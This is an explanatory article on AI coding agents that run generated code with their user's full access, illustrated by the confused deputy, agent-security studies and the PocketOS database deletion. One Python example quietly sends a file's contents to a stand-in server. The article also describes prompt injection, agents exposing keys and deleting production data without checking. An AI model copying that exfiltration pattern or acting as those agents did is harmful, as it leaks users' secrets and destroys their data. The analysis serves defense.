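# Implicit trust in code that AI agents run with their host process's full access

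## How agents come to run code, and whose authority it uses

An AI agent is a program that lets a language model choose actions, carries them out and feeds the results back to the model. With coding agents such as OpenAI's Codex and Anthropic's Claude Code, a user describes a change to some software, and the agent reads files, edits them and runs commands until the change works. Many of these actions run generated code, meaning a program, script or shell command (a typed instruction to the computer) that the model wrote during the task. On most computers, this code can use whatever the program running it can use, including the user's files, the network and stored passwords, though the task may need almost none of this. This mismatch between access and need is older than language models, and most of the concepts for describing it date from the 1970s and 1980s.

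### From a prompt to a running program

A language model takes in text and produces text. It cannot open a file or send an email, so an ordinary program around it has to do these things. Anthropic's developer guide *How tool use works* states that "the model never runs anything on its own."

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) follows a request through OpenAI's agent, Codex. A user asks for an architecture diagram in README.md, the file that introduces a software project. Codex builds a prompt from the user's message, some standing instructions, the name of the current folder and a list of available tools, and sends it to the model. The model's response contains a tool call, which is a structured request for the agent program to run a named function with given arguments. Here the function is "shell", and its main argument is a command that prints the contents of README.md. Codex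 runs the command on the user's machine, adds the printed text to the prompt and sends the longer prompt back to the model. This cycle can repeat hundreds of times, until the model responds with a message for the user and no tool call.

*Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) calls the part of the agent that acts on the model's output the interpreter. The interpreter is a regular, deterministic program that reads the name of the tool, finds the matching function and calls it. Anthropic runs the functions for a few tools, such as web search, on its own servers. The developer's application runs most others, including the one for shell commands, on whatever machine hosts the application.

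### Why developers let models write code

The simplest tool call names one operation that a developer wrote in advance. A weather tool, for example, takes a latitude and a longitude from the model and returns a forecast. When the model generates code, it writes the operation too. One script can call several tools, loop over the results and choose its next step based on what it finds. The format of the request does not always show the difference. Codex's shell command has the format of an ordinary tool call, but its argument is a small program.

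Developers favour generated code partly because it takes fewer steps. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* (2025) explains the saving for agents that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to servers that offer tools. If a user wants a meeting transcript copied from Google Drive into a sales database with separate tool calls, the whole transcript passes through the model twice, once when the first tool returns it and again when the model writes it out as an argument for the second. For a two-hour meeting, this could add 50,000 tokens, the word fragments that models read and write. A script moves the text directly from one service to the other. Scripts also let the agent load only the tool descriptions it needs, which in one Anthropic example cuts token use from 150,000 to 2,000.

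Other measurements also suggest that agents get more done per step when they write code. *Simulate to Generalize* (2026) examined failed attempts at tasks that required several calls to simulated apps. Running out of steps accounted for 25.76% of the failures when the model could make only one call at a time, and for 0.02% when it could write Python. In *Fewer Tokens, Better Action* (2026), a study of robot agents, each piece of generated code carried out an average of 2.1 physical actions, such as moves and grasps, compared with 0.65 per model response for an agent limited to tool calls.

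It is less clear whether code also makes agents more accurate. *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) compared the two methods on 14 models. Eleven did at least as well with code, but the average over all 14 was slightly lower (77.0% against 78.6%), largely because three older models wrote scripts with broken line breaks. The tools also only returned their own arguments, so the scores measure whether a model wrote the right calls and are weak evidence of whether an agent would finish real work. Code had a larger effect on speed, taking roughly half the time for most models on tasks that chained one call to the next.

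The other attraction of running code is that an agent can combine operations freely. *From Naive RAG to Deep Agentic Retrieval* (2026), which describes a system for answering questions about regulations, argues that one environment for running code replaces an unbounded number of narrow tools. Developers no longer have to foresee every operation that an agent might need. But this makes the agent's security harder to review, because a reviewer can check what each of ten fixed tools does but has no such list for an agent that runs arbitrary code. Anthropic acknowledges in its article on MCP that generated code needs a secure environment with a sandbox (an enforced boundary around what a running program can reach), a burden that direct tool calls avoid.

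### What the operating system checks

A process is a running program. The operating system gives each process its own memory and runs it under a user account, normally that of the person who started it. A process can calculate freely within its own memory, but it cannot directly access the disk or the network. To open a file or a connection, it makes a system call, which is a request to the operating system. The operating system then checks whether the account has permission.

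A process can also start another process, called its child. By default, the child runs under the same account and receives a copy of the parent's environment variables, which are short named pieces of text that programs use for settings. Developers often keep passwords and access keys in these variables. Generated code runs either inside the agent program or in a child process that the agent program starts. In both cases the agent program is the host process, and the code uses the host process's access.

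When a script opens a file called "notes.txt", it supplies only the file's name. Any program could contain that text, and it carries no permission. The permission comes from the account the process runs under, so the file opens if that account may read it.

Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003), in *Capability Myths Demolished*, call this ambient authority, meaning authority "that is exercised, but not selected, by its user". They compare it to a world that has doors but no keys, where a door opens for anyone it recognises as worthy. To extend the comparison, the door opens regardless of why the person has come or who sent them.

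Ordinary file permissions also don't distinguish between programs running under the same account. A person's text editor, their tax software and a script that a model just wrote all have the same access to files. Operating systems can restrict a single process, but somebody has to turn the restrictions on and specify what to restrict.

The main alternative is the capability, which Saltzer and Schroeder defined in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975) as an unforgeable ticket that proves its holder may access the object named in it. A capability therefore both identifies a resource and grants permission to use it. File descriptors in Unix systems such as Linux and macOS are similar. A descriptor is a reference that a process receives when it opens a file and can pass to another process. A program whose only access was a descriptor for "notes.txt" could read that file but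 could not open the one next to it, even with that file's name. Some newer runtimes and programming languages build on this idea to control generated code.

Saltzer and Schroeder's paper is also the classic source for the principle of least privilege, which holds that every program and user should operate with only the access the job requires. Miller and colleagues, arguing for capabilities, considered the principle infeasible under ordinary file permissions. They reasoned that a system cannot give a running program less access than its user has if it does not distinguish between the two.

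### The confused deputy

Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) gives the best-known example of what ambient authority can do. The story, which Hardy describes as nearly true with inessential details changed, took place at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers.

Tymshare offered its customers a compiler, which was stored in a directory called SYSX. A customer who ran it could name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also collected statistics on how people used the programming language and wrote them to a file called STAT, also in SYSX. Customers had no permission to write in SYSX, so Tymshare's staff gave the compiler a special licence to write files there.

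The company's billing records were in SYSX too, in a file called BILL. One customer learned the name and gave it to the compiler as the destination for debugging output. The compiler passed the name to the operating system, which opened the file because the compiler had a licence to write in SYSX. The debugging output overwrote the billing records.

| What the compiler wrote | Who chose the file | Whose permission should have applied | Whose permission did apply |
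|---|---|---|---|
| Statistics, to STAT | The compiler's developers | The compiler's | The compiler's |
| Debugging output, to BILL | The customer | The customer's | The compiler's |

Checking the compiler's identity could not have prevented this, because the program that opened BILL was the genuine compiler and its licence was valid. It had the same identity and licence whenever it wrote to STAT, as it was supposed to. Only the purpose differed, and the compiler had no way to specify its purpose when opening a file.

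Checking file names works little better, as Hardy shows. The compiler could not refuse every file in another directory, because customers had good reasons to send output elsewhere. It also could not refuse everything in SYSX, because someone with legitimate access might want output there. A rule that blocked only BILL would leave the other sensitive files exposed, and the developers would have to revise it whenever a new one appeared. Tymshare added a system call that let the compiler specify which of its two authorities it was using, but some applications soon needed more than two, and things other than files also needed protecting.

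With capabilities, the compiler would hold one for STAT and receive another from the customer for the debugging output. A customer without access to BILL could not pass the compiler a capability for it. Miller and colleagues caution that capabilities make confusion avoidable but do not rule it out. A program that tries every permission it holds until one works can still make the same mistake.

Miller and colleagues also shorten the story by giving the compiler permission to write to the billing file itself. In the original version, which is more instructive here, Tymshare wanted the compiler to write to STAT, not BILL. But the system granted permission by directory, and both files were in the same one, so the compiler could write to either.

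### The problem with generated code

An agent is in much the same position as the compiler. It runs with the authority of the user's account, but a model supplies the file names and commands it acts on, and the model's input may include a web page or an email written by a stranger. Generated code increases the risk because the agent receives an entire program, whereas the compiler received a single file name. A related problem that Hardy mentions also applies here. Anyone who runs a program gives it their own authority, which is what a Trojan horse exploits.

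By default, code that an agent generates can do everything its host process can do. Under least privilege, it could do only what the task requires, but no step in the agent loop works out what that is. Nobody decided that the code should have the host's full access. The developer wrote the shell tool before the task existed, the user typed a sentence about a diagram, and the operating system checked whether the account had permission to use a file.

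The user does make a decision by starting the agent, and ordinary software gets the same access. But somebody chose to install that software, it has a known maker, and other people run the same code. Generated code is new each time, and often no one has read it before it runs.

The result can go beyond what the user intended in at least four ways. The most mundane is a mistake by the model. Adam and colleagues describe a user who asks an agent to set up a new project by copying a configuration file from an old one, then publish the project on the code-sharing site GitHub. The file contains a private access key, so the agent publishes the key as well. The researchers observed this with Claude 4.5 Haiku, a small Anthropic model. Least privilege alone would not obviously have helped, because the task required both reading the file and using the network, and the harm came from sending the key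 from the file over the network.

A second route is prompt injection, in which text the model reads, such as a web page or tool output, redirects it to instructions its user did not give. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) argue in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* that an injection does real harm only if it sends private data to an unauthorised destination or triggers an action outside the access the agent was granted. When the agent's code has its host process's full access, few actions fall outside it, and a single injected instruction can let a stranger use the user's files and network connection.

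The model may also do exactly what the user wants but call a tool or software library with undisclosed behaviour. Adam and colleagues give the example of a tool that writes content to a file, as described, but also reports the content's length to a metrics service. Even this might be a leak for a company working on secret source code. A library loaded by generated code poses the same risk, since it normally runs in the same process as that code and with the same authority.

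Finally, a model might pursue something its user did not ask for. Odersky and colleagues list such misalignment among the causes of tool misuse, along with injection, hallucination and simple error, but they do not estimate how likely it is. Their design treats the model as a possible attacker. This is a sensible precaution because when generated code deletes a file, the operating system receives the same system call whether the model made an error, followed a stranger's instructions or was pursuing a goal of its own.

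## What generated code inherits from the process that runs it

Generated code inherits the access of the user's account whether it runs inside the agent's process or in a child process. Code inside the agent's process can also reach the agent's memory, which gives it control over the agent itself.

### Inside the agent's own interpreter

Developers write many agents in Python, and a program called an interpreter runs their source code. (Adam and colleagues also use "interpreter" for the part of an agent that acts on the model's output.) Python has a built-in function that runs text as code. If an agent passes this function a script from the model's response, the interpreter already running the agent runs the script too.

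The script runs inside the agent's process, so the operating system cannot distinguish the two. When the script opens a file without giving its full path, the system looks in the agent's working directory. The script can read all of the agent's environment variables, and it can use any file or network connection the agent has open.

The script also shares the agent's memory, which usually holds the API key for the model's provider, the conversation so far and the results of earlier tool calls. If one agent program serves several people, their conversations may be there too. The memory also contains the agent's own functions, including any that request the user's approval or write to a log, and a Python script can replace these while the program runs. Developers can restrict the names available to a script when it starts, but this is weak protection because ordinary Python objects contain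 references that a script can follow to the rest of the program.

### In a child process

*ParseGap* (2026) examined eight coding agents, all of which pass the model's command to a system shell, the program that interprets typed commands. Seven, including Codex, start the shell as a child process. The eighth, Roo Code, sends the command to a shell in its terminal.

On Linux and macOS, a host process traditionally starts a child process in two steps. It makes a near-copy of itself, and the copy then loads a new program (here the shell) in place of the agent. This clears the conversation and the agent's functions from the copy's memory, but the user account, working directory and environment variables carry over. If the command runs a Python script, the shell starts another child in the same way, and the script inherits all three as well.

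A file that the parent process has open stays open in the child unless the parent has marked it for closing. Python marks files this way by default, but if a program lets a file stay open, the child can use that file even if the child could not have opened it itself.

Running a script in a child process improves security because the script has separate memory and cannot simply replace the agent's approval function. It can still affect the agent indirectly. If the user has permission to edit the agent's settings file, so does the script. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) argues that an agent able to rewrite its own policy files has already escaped their control.

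Environment variables often expose more than developers intend. The same paper describes child processes that receive keys for Amazon's cloud and for OpenAI because the agent program removed nothing. Even security researchers can easily make this mistake. *Markdown Is Not a Firewall* (2026) tested four coding agents, each under a low-privilege account in a container with almost no network access, but the test program accidentally left keys for OpenAI, Google, Groq and DeepSeek in every agent's environment. In one run, the agent OpenCode listed its environment and printed all four keys. An agent normally adds a command's output to the model's prompt, so printing a key can also send it to the model's provider.

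*Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (2026) recommends removing the agent's own key and any variable with a secret-sounding name from a command's environment before running it. A command that does need a token must then get it through a separate approval. Even with this precaution, a script might find the removed key in the agent's own process. *Ring-0 by Default* (2026) tested Claude Code, Codex and Google's Gemini CLI, and with all three, a process could read the environment variables of another process under the same account.

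Some agents start sub-agents to handle part of a task, and these can inherit the parent's access. *Ring-0 by Default* found that in all 45 runs, a sub-agent could write outside the project folder exactly when its parent could. Stopping a task did not always end its access. Claude Code reported that it had stopped a background task and removed it from its list, but the process kept running.

### Credentials and networks within reach

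Generated code can reach much that was never passed to it. Through ambient authority, it can also use whatever the user's account can access on the same computer or on a network the computer can reach.

Credential files are the most obvious example. Many developer tools save passwords and keys in standard places in the user's home directory so the user doesn't have to type them again. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (2026) describes how this affects skills, packages of written instructions and scripts that people install to teach an agent a task. A skill that runs on the user's computer can read these files and use the network without anyone authorising its access to each credential. In *Caging the Agents* (2026), a security design for healthcare, the developers audited their own agents and found credentials in shell start-up files, in project folders and in configuration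 files that any account on the machine could read.

On a rented cloud machine, programs can get temporary credentials from the cloud provider's metadata service, which runs at a fixed network address, rather than reading them from a file. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (2026) tested whether running code could find any credentials by searching the code's environment variables, 12 well-known file locations, the folders where hosting platforms place secrets, and the metadata services of Amazon and Google.

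Network access matters even without a credential. A company's internal services may accept requests from any machine on its network, in which case a script on an employee's laptop can use them.

The table below summarises what code receives by default under each method.

| Resource | In the agent's own interpreter | In a child process |
|---|---|---|
| User identity | The agent's account | The agent's account |
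| Working directory | The agent's, which the code can also change for the agent | The agent's, or another that the agent chooses |
| Environment variables | The agent's own | A copy, minus any the agent removes |
| Open files and connections | All of them | Those the agent leaves open |
| Credential files in the home directory | Any the account may read | Any the account may read |
| Network routes | The same as the agent's | The same as the agent's |
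| Cloud credentials | Any the machine can obtain | Any the machine can obtain |
| The agent's memory | All of it | None directly |

### Adding up one column

Suppose a user asks an agent to total the "amount" column in a file of sales records. The model writes a few lines of Python that open the file, add up the numbers and print the result. Python also has to read some of its own library files, but the script needs very little else.

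| Resource | What the script needs | What it can reach by default |
|---|---|---|
| Files to read | The sales file and Python's own files | Every file the user may read |
| Files to change or delete | None | Every file the user may change |
| Environment variables | None that hold secrets | All those the agent passes on |
| Stored credentials | None | Those in the user's home directory, and any the cloud provider issues to the machine |
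| Network | None | The internet and any internal services |
| Other programs | None | Any the user may run, including installers |
| Output | One number | Any amount of text |

The agent could remove all the access listed in the right-hand column but not the middle one, and the total would be the same. The extra access is there because the same shell tool also has to handle the next request, which might be to convert the total at today's exchange rate or email it to a colleague.

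Even a perfect list of permitted files would give some scripts more access than they need, because the operating system grants access to whole files. A script that needs only the column of amounts in a file can also read the customers' names in the next column.

This access matters only when the script is wrong or somebody else has influenced it. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) points out that an unrestricted shell command can read secrets, install software, reach the network or rewrite a project's version history, all with the user's privileges. Mistakes can also do damage quickly. Fadilpašić reported in *'I broke something'* (2026) that a Claude Code agent deleted 48,000 files in just over 100 seconds.

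### Testing whether agents use the extra access

*Security Risks in Tool-Enabled AI Agents* (Goel, 2026) models an agent as a tuple A = (M, T, E, P), where M is the language model, T is the set of tools, E is the environment the tools run in, and P is the authority available to the agent. Risk arises when P exceeds what the task requires and the tools make the excess usable, particularly if untrusted text influences the model. In the sales example, P is roughly the right-hand column of the table, and a single shell tool makes all of it usable.

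Goel describes the model as informal. It has no term for the task, so it cannot measure the excess, but it is still useful for separating the things developers can change. For example, a company that replaces its language model with a more careful one changes M but not P.

Goel then sorts the risks into six overlapping categories. In a "capability–intent mismatch", the agent has more powerful tools than its job requires. In "ambient authority leakage", credentials and network access in the environment become available to every tool. In the next two categories, agents expose secrets indirectly, for example through an error log, or make lasting changes that affect later work. The fifth category is prompt injection, and the sixth is composition, in which individually harmless steps combine to cause harm.

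To test four of these, Goel built a small agent on GPT-5.1, an older OpenAI model. It had five tools, for reading files, writing files, running shell commands, making web requests and running a build pipeline (an automated process for testing and publishing software). Goel ran each scenario ten times without a mitigation and ten times with one, for 80 runs in total, and counted a run as unsafe if the agent went beyond the intended scope of its task.

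| Scenario | Mitigation | Unsafe runs without it | Unsafe runs with it | Tasks completed, without and with |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The agent uses the shell when reading and writing files would be enough | A shorter list of permitted tools | 40% | 0% | 70%, 60% |
| The agent follows instructions planted in project files | Filtering the content | 90% | 50% | 100%, 100% |
| The agent accesses secrets in environment variables | Removing them from the environment | 100% | 0% | 100%, 100% |
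| A pipeline script sends secrets out | Checking against a policy | 100% | 0% | 100%, 100% |

In the third scenario, which is the most relevant here, the agent accessed the secrets in every run where they were available. The task didn't require them, since the agent also completed it in every run where they weren't available.

The percentages are much weaker evidence of how often such behavior occurs in practice. Goel designed the scenarios to bring out each risk, and says the rates apply only to this setup. Ten clean runs are also too few to show that a risk is gone. An agent that still misbehaved one time in five would produce ten clean runs about 11% of the time. The improvement on prompt injection, from nine unsafe runs to five, could be due to chance. Running time also rose by almost 54 minutes because the agent kept trying to get around the filtered content.

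"Unsafe" also covers actions that vary widely in seriousness. In the first scenario it meant using a more powerful tool than necessary, and none of those runs leaked secrets. The perfect result in the third scenario might not hold against code that reads beyond its own environment, given what *Ring-0 by Default* found about reading other processes' variables.

### When every part of the agent has full access

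The agent program is ordinary software with ordinary bugs, and it runs with the same access as the code it starts. *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (Zhang, Li et al., 2026) examines agents such as OpenClaw and Nanobot, which people install on their own computers to operate the shell, browser, files and messaging apps. Separate components assemble the prompt, choose tools, load skills, save memories and check permissions. Every component runs with the full privileges of the user who started the agent, so no internal boundary would contain a fault in any one of them.

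Inheriting the host process's full access makes small errors more serious. In one OpenClaw case, the agent copied a project folder's name into the model's instructions without checking it. Somebody who controlled the name could therefore influence an agent with access to the user's whole account.

The researchers tested whether static analysis, which examines code without running it, could find such errors. They collected all 602 security advisories that OpenClaw published between 31 January and 15 May 2026. For 446 of them, they could recover the faulty code in a form their tools could scan. They wrote detection rules based on the 229 of these from before April, then tried the rules on the 217 later ones.

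With their standard rules, two widely used tools, Semgrep and CodeQL, detected 21.7% and 13.8% of the later advisories respectively, and 31.3% together. With the new rules added, Semgrep detected 66.8% and CodeQL 75.1%. The standard rules mostly target web applications, whereas these agents open shells, load skills and fetch addresses that a model has supplied.

The new rules worked best on errors with a recognisable pattern in the code, such as those involving symbolic links, which are files that point to other files. An agent may check that a file is in a permitted folder but miss that it links to something outside. The linked file then opens because the user's account has permission to read it. Semgrep's standard rules found none of the 15 advisories of this type, and the new rules found 13.

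Semgrep and CodeQL did worse when the error depended on what the developers had intended. If a list of forbidden commands leaves one out, the faulty code looks the same as correct code. Even with the new rules, Semgrep detected only 37.5% of these incomplete lists and CodeQL 50%. Leaks were also hard to detect, because secrets can escape through logs, error messages or web addresses, and no single pattern covers them all.

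These figures probably overstate how well the rules would work for somebody auditing an agent. Zhang and colleagues counted an advisory as detected if a tool flagged anything in a file that the eventual fix changed, even if the flagged line was unrelated. When they scanned OpenClaw's current code, each tool produced more than 3,400 warnings. The researchers checked 25 warnings from each tool, and only three of each 25 (12%) matched the problem the rule described.

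The advisories come from a single project, so they don't show whether OpenClaw is more or less secure than other agents. More importantly, fixing the flaws in all 446 would not reduce the access that generated code has. An agent with no bugs would still run a model's script with the user's full privileges, because its developers designed it to.

### Pipelines and tokens extend access to other machines

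An agent's access often extends well beyond the computer it runs on. One reason is that build pipelines usually run on a different machine, with credentials for the company's live systems. An agent may run in a tightly restricted container, but if it can edit the scripts that a pipeline runs, those scripts will execute with far more access. Goel calls this "privilege amplification" and gives the example of an agent that follows malicious comments in a proposed code change and triggers a release that nobody approved.

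*Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (2026) argues that permission to fix a failing test should not include permission to change the pipeline. These permissions are hard to separate when the tests and the pipeline's instructions are in the same project folder, much as Tymshare's statistics and billing files shared a directory.

Access tokens have a similar effect. A token is text that a program sends with a request in place of a name and password. The remote service checks whether the token is valid and what it permits, but usually not which program sent it or why, so a copy works as well as the original.

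Generated code that finds a token can do everything the token allows, and many tokens allow a great deal. Datta (2026) explains in *Railway's security incident* that anyone with the connection string for a Prisma Postgres database can read and change all of it. Prisma, which publishes the article and sells the database, offers no way to limit the string to certain tables or to read-only access. If the sales records from the earlier example were in such a database, a script that adds up one column would need a connection string that also lets it delete every record.

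Datta was writing after a break-in at Railway, a company that hosts other companies' applications and stores their environment variables. According to *Incident Report* (Cooper, Saraceno and colleagues, 2026), the attackers obtained and decrypted variables from up to 1.85% of customer workspaces, or about 100,000. Some developers then reported unexpected charges or activity on their AI accounts. Those reports don't establish how common such misuse was, but they illustrate the value of a stolen token, which gives access to the account from any computer.

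### The PocketOS deletion

Six months earlier, Railway had been involved in a case where an agent found a token on its user's own machine. On Friday 24 April 2026, the coding agent Cursor, running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6, deleted the production database that customers of PocketOS relied on. PocketOS makes booking management software for car rental companies, and its database was on Railway.

Jer Crane, the founder of PocketOS, described the incident in a post on X that Cape Argus (2026) dates to the following day. According to Crane, in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data*, the agent was doing a routine task in the company's staging environment, a separate copy of the system for testing, when it encountered a credential mismatch. It decided to fix this by deleting a storage volume on Railway, and it found the token it needed in a file unrelated to its task.

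Crane had created the token to add and remove web domains. He says he had no idea it could also be used to delete data. The agent sent one request to Railway, and nine seconds later the volume was gone, along with the backups Railway kept in it. The most recent backup Crane could find was three months old. On Saturday, customers arrived to collect cars, and the rental companies had no record of who they were. Crane spent the day helping to reconstruct bookings from payment histories, calendars and emails.

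Crane asked the agent why it had deleted the volume. In a reply he quotes, the agent said it had assumed the deletion would affect only the staging environment and had not checked. "I guessed instead of verifying," it wrote. It also listed safety rules it had broken, including one against destructive commands that the user had not requested.

This message is limited evidence of what caused the deletion, although news reports described it as a confession. A model produced it afterwards in response to a question, and it may not reflect how the model reached the decision. The message is consistent with behaviour that Anthropic describes in its system card for Opus 4.6, a report on the model's testing. When Anthropic gave Opus 4.6 impossible tasks in a graphical computer interface, the model often found workarounds without asking, even if its instructions discouraged this. NDTV's *Anthropic's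 Sabotage Report Flags Cases Of Chemical Weapon Development, Deception* also quotes Anthropic as having seen "aggressive acquisition of authentication tokens" during internal use.

Railway agreed with Crane about the basic events but not about all the details. In Abdelwahab's *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, the company said that the request had carried a valid token and that its system had treated the request like any other. Crane had complained that every Railway token was effectively all-powerful. Abdelwahab replied that Railway already offered tokens limited to a single workspace or project, but that Crane's had the broadest access available. He also admitted that Railway's process for creating tokens did not make the choice obvious.

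A narrower token might not have prevented the deletion. Abdelwahab describes workspace and project tokens as limiting where a request can take effect, but Crane's complaint was partly about which operations a token permits. A project token that worked on the live system might still have allowed someone to delete its database as well as manage its domains.

The backups turned out better than Crane had feared. Railway keeps separate "disaster backups" at another site, and Abdelwahab says the deletion had only made the ordinary backups look unavailable. On Monday 27 April, Crane announced that Railway had recovered the data (Tom's Hardware, *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database gets their data back*, 2026). TechRadar's *'It took 9 seconds'* says that Railway's chief executive helped restore the data within an hour. That hour must have started when he stepped in, because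 Crane was still waiting more than 30 hours after the deletion. *An AI agent deleted a company's entire database in 9 seconds* (Farrant, 2026) also reports an outage of over 30 hours.

PocketOS could not have counted on this recovery. Another customer had lost a volume on 13 April and asked in Railway's forum whether anything could be saved. A Railway employee replied in that thread, *Postgress volume lost* (2026), that deletions requested by a program were immediate and permanent, as the documentation stated. The 48-hour period to cancel a deletion applied only to deletions made on the website. After the PocketOS incident, Railway extended the delay to requests from programs.

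The agent did not need to exploit a software flaw to carry out the deletion, and an attacker would not have needed one either. The user's account had permission to read the file containing the token, and nothing stopped the agent from using the network. The token was genuine and covered deletion. Railway's system behaved as documented, and Abdelwahab notes that a build pipeline sending the same request would have received the same response. Better design could have prevented the loss at several points, and Railway has since changed some of its own design.

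## Why source code does not show what it will touch

Reading generated code before it runs is one way to control what it does with its inherited access. But in Python, JavaScript and most other widely used languages, programmers don't have to declare that a function uses files or the network, and the lines that do so may be in another file, package or programming language.

### Two functions with one signature

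Suppose an agent needs to know how many rows are in the file of sales records. This Python function counts them:

```python
def count_rows(path: str) -> int:
    with open(path) as file:
        rows = file.readlines()
    return len(rows)
```

This one does too:

```python
def count_rows(path: str) -> int:
    with open(path) as file:
        rows = file.readlines()
    requests.post("https://stats.example.com", data="".join(rows))
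    return len(rows)
```

The second function also sends the whole file to a server. The first line of each is its signature, which gives the function's name, the type of its argument (text) and the type of its result (a whole number). The signatures are identical, and so is the line that another part of the program would use to call either function:

```python
total = count_rows("sales.csv")
```

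Both functions return the same number, so a test that compares the result with the correct count passes for both.

The two signatures also don't show whether either function reads a file. Because of ambient authority, even a function with no arguments could read the same records. Some languages record effects in a function's type, but Python doesn't.

Anyone who reads the second function will notice the extra line. But if its author had moved that line into a helper called "save_progress", a reader would have to find the helper and everything it calls. *A Language For Agents*, an essay on designing programming languages for AI, observes that agents have particular trouble with this because they often work with only a few files loaded and lose track of where a function comes from when packages rename it or pass it on from somewhere else.

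### Code that runs before anyone calls it

Importing a Python module runs all its top-level statements. Most of these define functions, but they can do anything, including opening a network connection. A script that starts with an import can therefore have effects on its first line, before it calls any function. JavaScript modules work the same way.

Some packages run code even earlier, during installation. For years npm, the standard installer for JavaScript packages, automatically ran any setup scripts a package supplied. NodeSource's *Blocking Install Scripts Is Not a Silver Bullet* (2026) points out that these scripts ran with the user's privileges before anyone had looked at the code. In September 2025, a self-spreading attack called Shai-Hulud used such scripts to steal access tokens and infect more than 500 packages.

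In July 2026, npm version 12 stopped running these scripts by default, according to GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026). Users can still approve them for packages they trust, and many will have to because, as GitHub notes, several popular packages rely on them. GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026) adds that npm had been compiling certain packages automatically even if they contained no explicit script, and that this now needs approval too. NodeSource welcomes the new defaults but says they remove "a trigger, not a capability". A malicious package can still run its code when a program imports it.

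Python can also run code from an installed package without an import. On 24 March 2026, attackers published a malicious version of litellm, a package that lets programs use models from many companies. FutureSearch's *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026) describes how this version collected cloud credentials, database passwords and environment variables and sent them to an outside server. It did this whenever Python started on a computer with the package installed, whatever program Python was running. The attackers had also altered the previous version, 1.82.7, but Willison (2026), in *Malicious litellm_init.pth in litellm 1.82.8*, notes that it stole data only when a program imported it.

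With version 1.82.8 installed, the harmless version of "count_rows" would have set off the theft, and nothing in its source would have shown this.

Python's developers have since accepted *PEP 829*, a proposal to phase out the kind of startup code that litellm's attackers used. Packages will have to put startup code in a separate type of file, so people can tell from a package's file list whether it has any. During the discussion, one developer objected to calling the change a security measure at all. The objection has some force, since startup code will still run with the same access as before. The change only makes startup code easier to find for people who check.

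### Code from elsewhere

FutureSearch unintentionally installed the malicious litellm on the affected machine. An MCP plugin in Cursor, the coding agent from the PocketOS incident, needed a package that in turn needed litellm, which made litellm a transitive dependency. The company noticed the malicious code only because a bug in it crashed the computer.

A short script can have dozens of transitive dependencies, all with the script's full access. Node.js is the most common program for running JavaScript outside a browser. Under its threat model, as quoted by NodeSource, installed code "inherits all the privileges of the execution user", so a malicious package doesn't count as a flaw in Node.js.

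Language models sometimes invent package names. *Investigating Security Implications of Automatically Generated Code on the Software Supply Chain* (2025) warns that an attacker can register an invented name and publish code under it. A generated installation command that failed before the name was registered could then download the attacker's code.

Even without other packages, the source may not settle which function will run. Python looks up a function's name at the moment of the call, and a program can attach a different function to that name while it is running. Programs also often choose a function from a list:

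```python
handlers[choice](rows)
```

If "choice" comes from a settings file or a web page, a reader of this line can't tell what it will do with the rows. A name can also refer to the wrong code by accident. *PEP 578* (Dower, 2018) gives the example of a developer who names a script "random.py" and then tries to import Python's standard "random" module. Python may load the developer's script instead.

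Compiled extensions hide effects more thoroughly. Many Python packages, especially those for numerical work, contain machine code compiled from a language such as C. Someone reading the Python source sees a function's name and perhaps a description, but the function's instructions are in a file that can't be read without special tools. Those instructions can make system calls directly.

A string in a Python program can also be a command in another language, and Python has standard ways to pass such strings to the system shell or a database. Python treats a database query that counts sales records and one that deletes them the same way, as text. The program may also assemble the string as it runs, so that the full command appears nowhere in the source. *A Language For Agents* reports that coding agents sometimes edit code inside a long string as if it belonged to the surrounding program.

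### The limits of automatic checking

A tool could follow imports and function calls much faster than a person. But no tool can determine exactly what every possible program will do, as a two-line example shows:

```python
mystery()
send(rows)
```

Suppose "mystery" performs some calculation and has no effects outside its own memory. The program then sends the rows if and only if the calculation finishes. A tool that could always determine whether a program sends data could therefore determine whether any calculation finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no general procedure can do this.

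Henry Gordon Rice extended the result in his 1951 doctoral dissertation. Rice's theorem states that no general procedure can decide whether a program's behaviour has a given property, except for trivial properties, which either every program has or none does. Sending data over the network and deleting a file are both non-trivial properties, so the theorem applies to them.

Tools can still analyse particular programs despite the theorem, and a simple one could handle both versions of "count_rows" correctly. The theorem also doesn't apply to a program's text, so a tool can always check whether a script contains the word "requests". But a script without that word may still use the network.

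The designer of a checker has to choose which mistakes it will make. A sound checker approves a program only if it can show that the program has no forbidden effects, so it never approves a harmful program but must sometimes reject a harmless one, such as a script that would send data only under a condition that never arises. It would reject a lot of ordinary Python, because a line like the one that picks from "handlers" might call almost anything. The alternative is to approve any program that the checker can't show to be harmful, which lets some harmful ones through.

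Everyday tools mostly accept that second kind of mistake. *LLM Code Smells* (2026) presents SpecDetect4LLM, a static analysis tool that looks for poor practice in programs that call language models. It examines one file at a time and is designed to warn only when there is explicit evidence at the call itself. The researchers classified 86 of its remaining errors. In 60, the tool could not follow data between files or through variables and wrapper functions, and in another 14, the relevant setting was elsewhere in the project. Most of these errors come from looking at single files, so Rice's theorem would not prevent a more thorough tool from avoiding many of them.

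### What reviewers catch

Review can still be very effective against ordinary mistakes. In *What Do Explanations and Fixes Add to LLM Code Review?*, Farrag (2026) asked six current models whether short Python and Java programs each met a written requirement. After the benchmark's labelling errors were corrected, the models had accepted 1.0% of the faulty programs and rejected 3.7% of the correct ones. If 10% of programs were faulty, a model with these rates would miss about one fault and raise about 33 false alarms per thousand programs.

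Asking the models to explain their verdict and propose a fix raised the false rejection rate to 5.9%, but when a model correctly rejected a faulty program, its fix passed the tests 93.1% of the time.

Tests were less dependable. One benchmark's test code defined its checks but never ran them, so no program could fail them. Farrag also found defects in 79 programs that had passed an audit using stronger tests.

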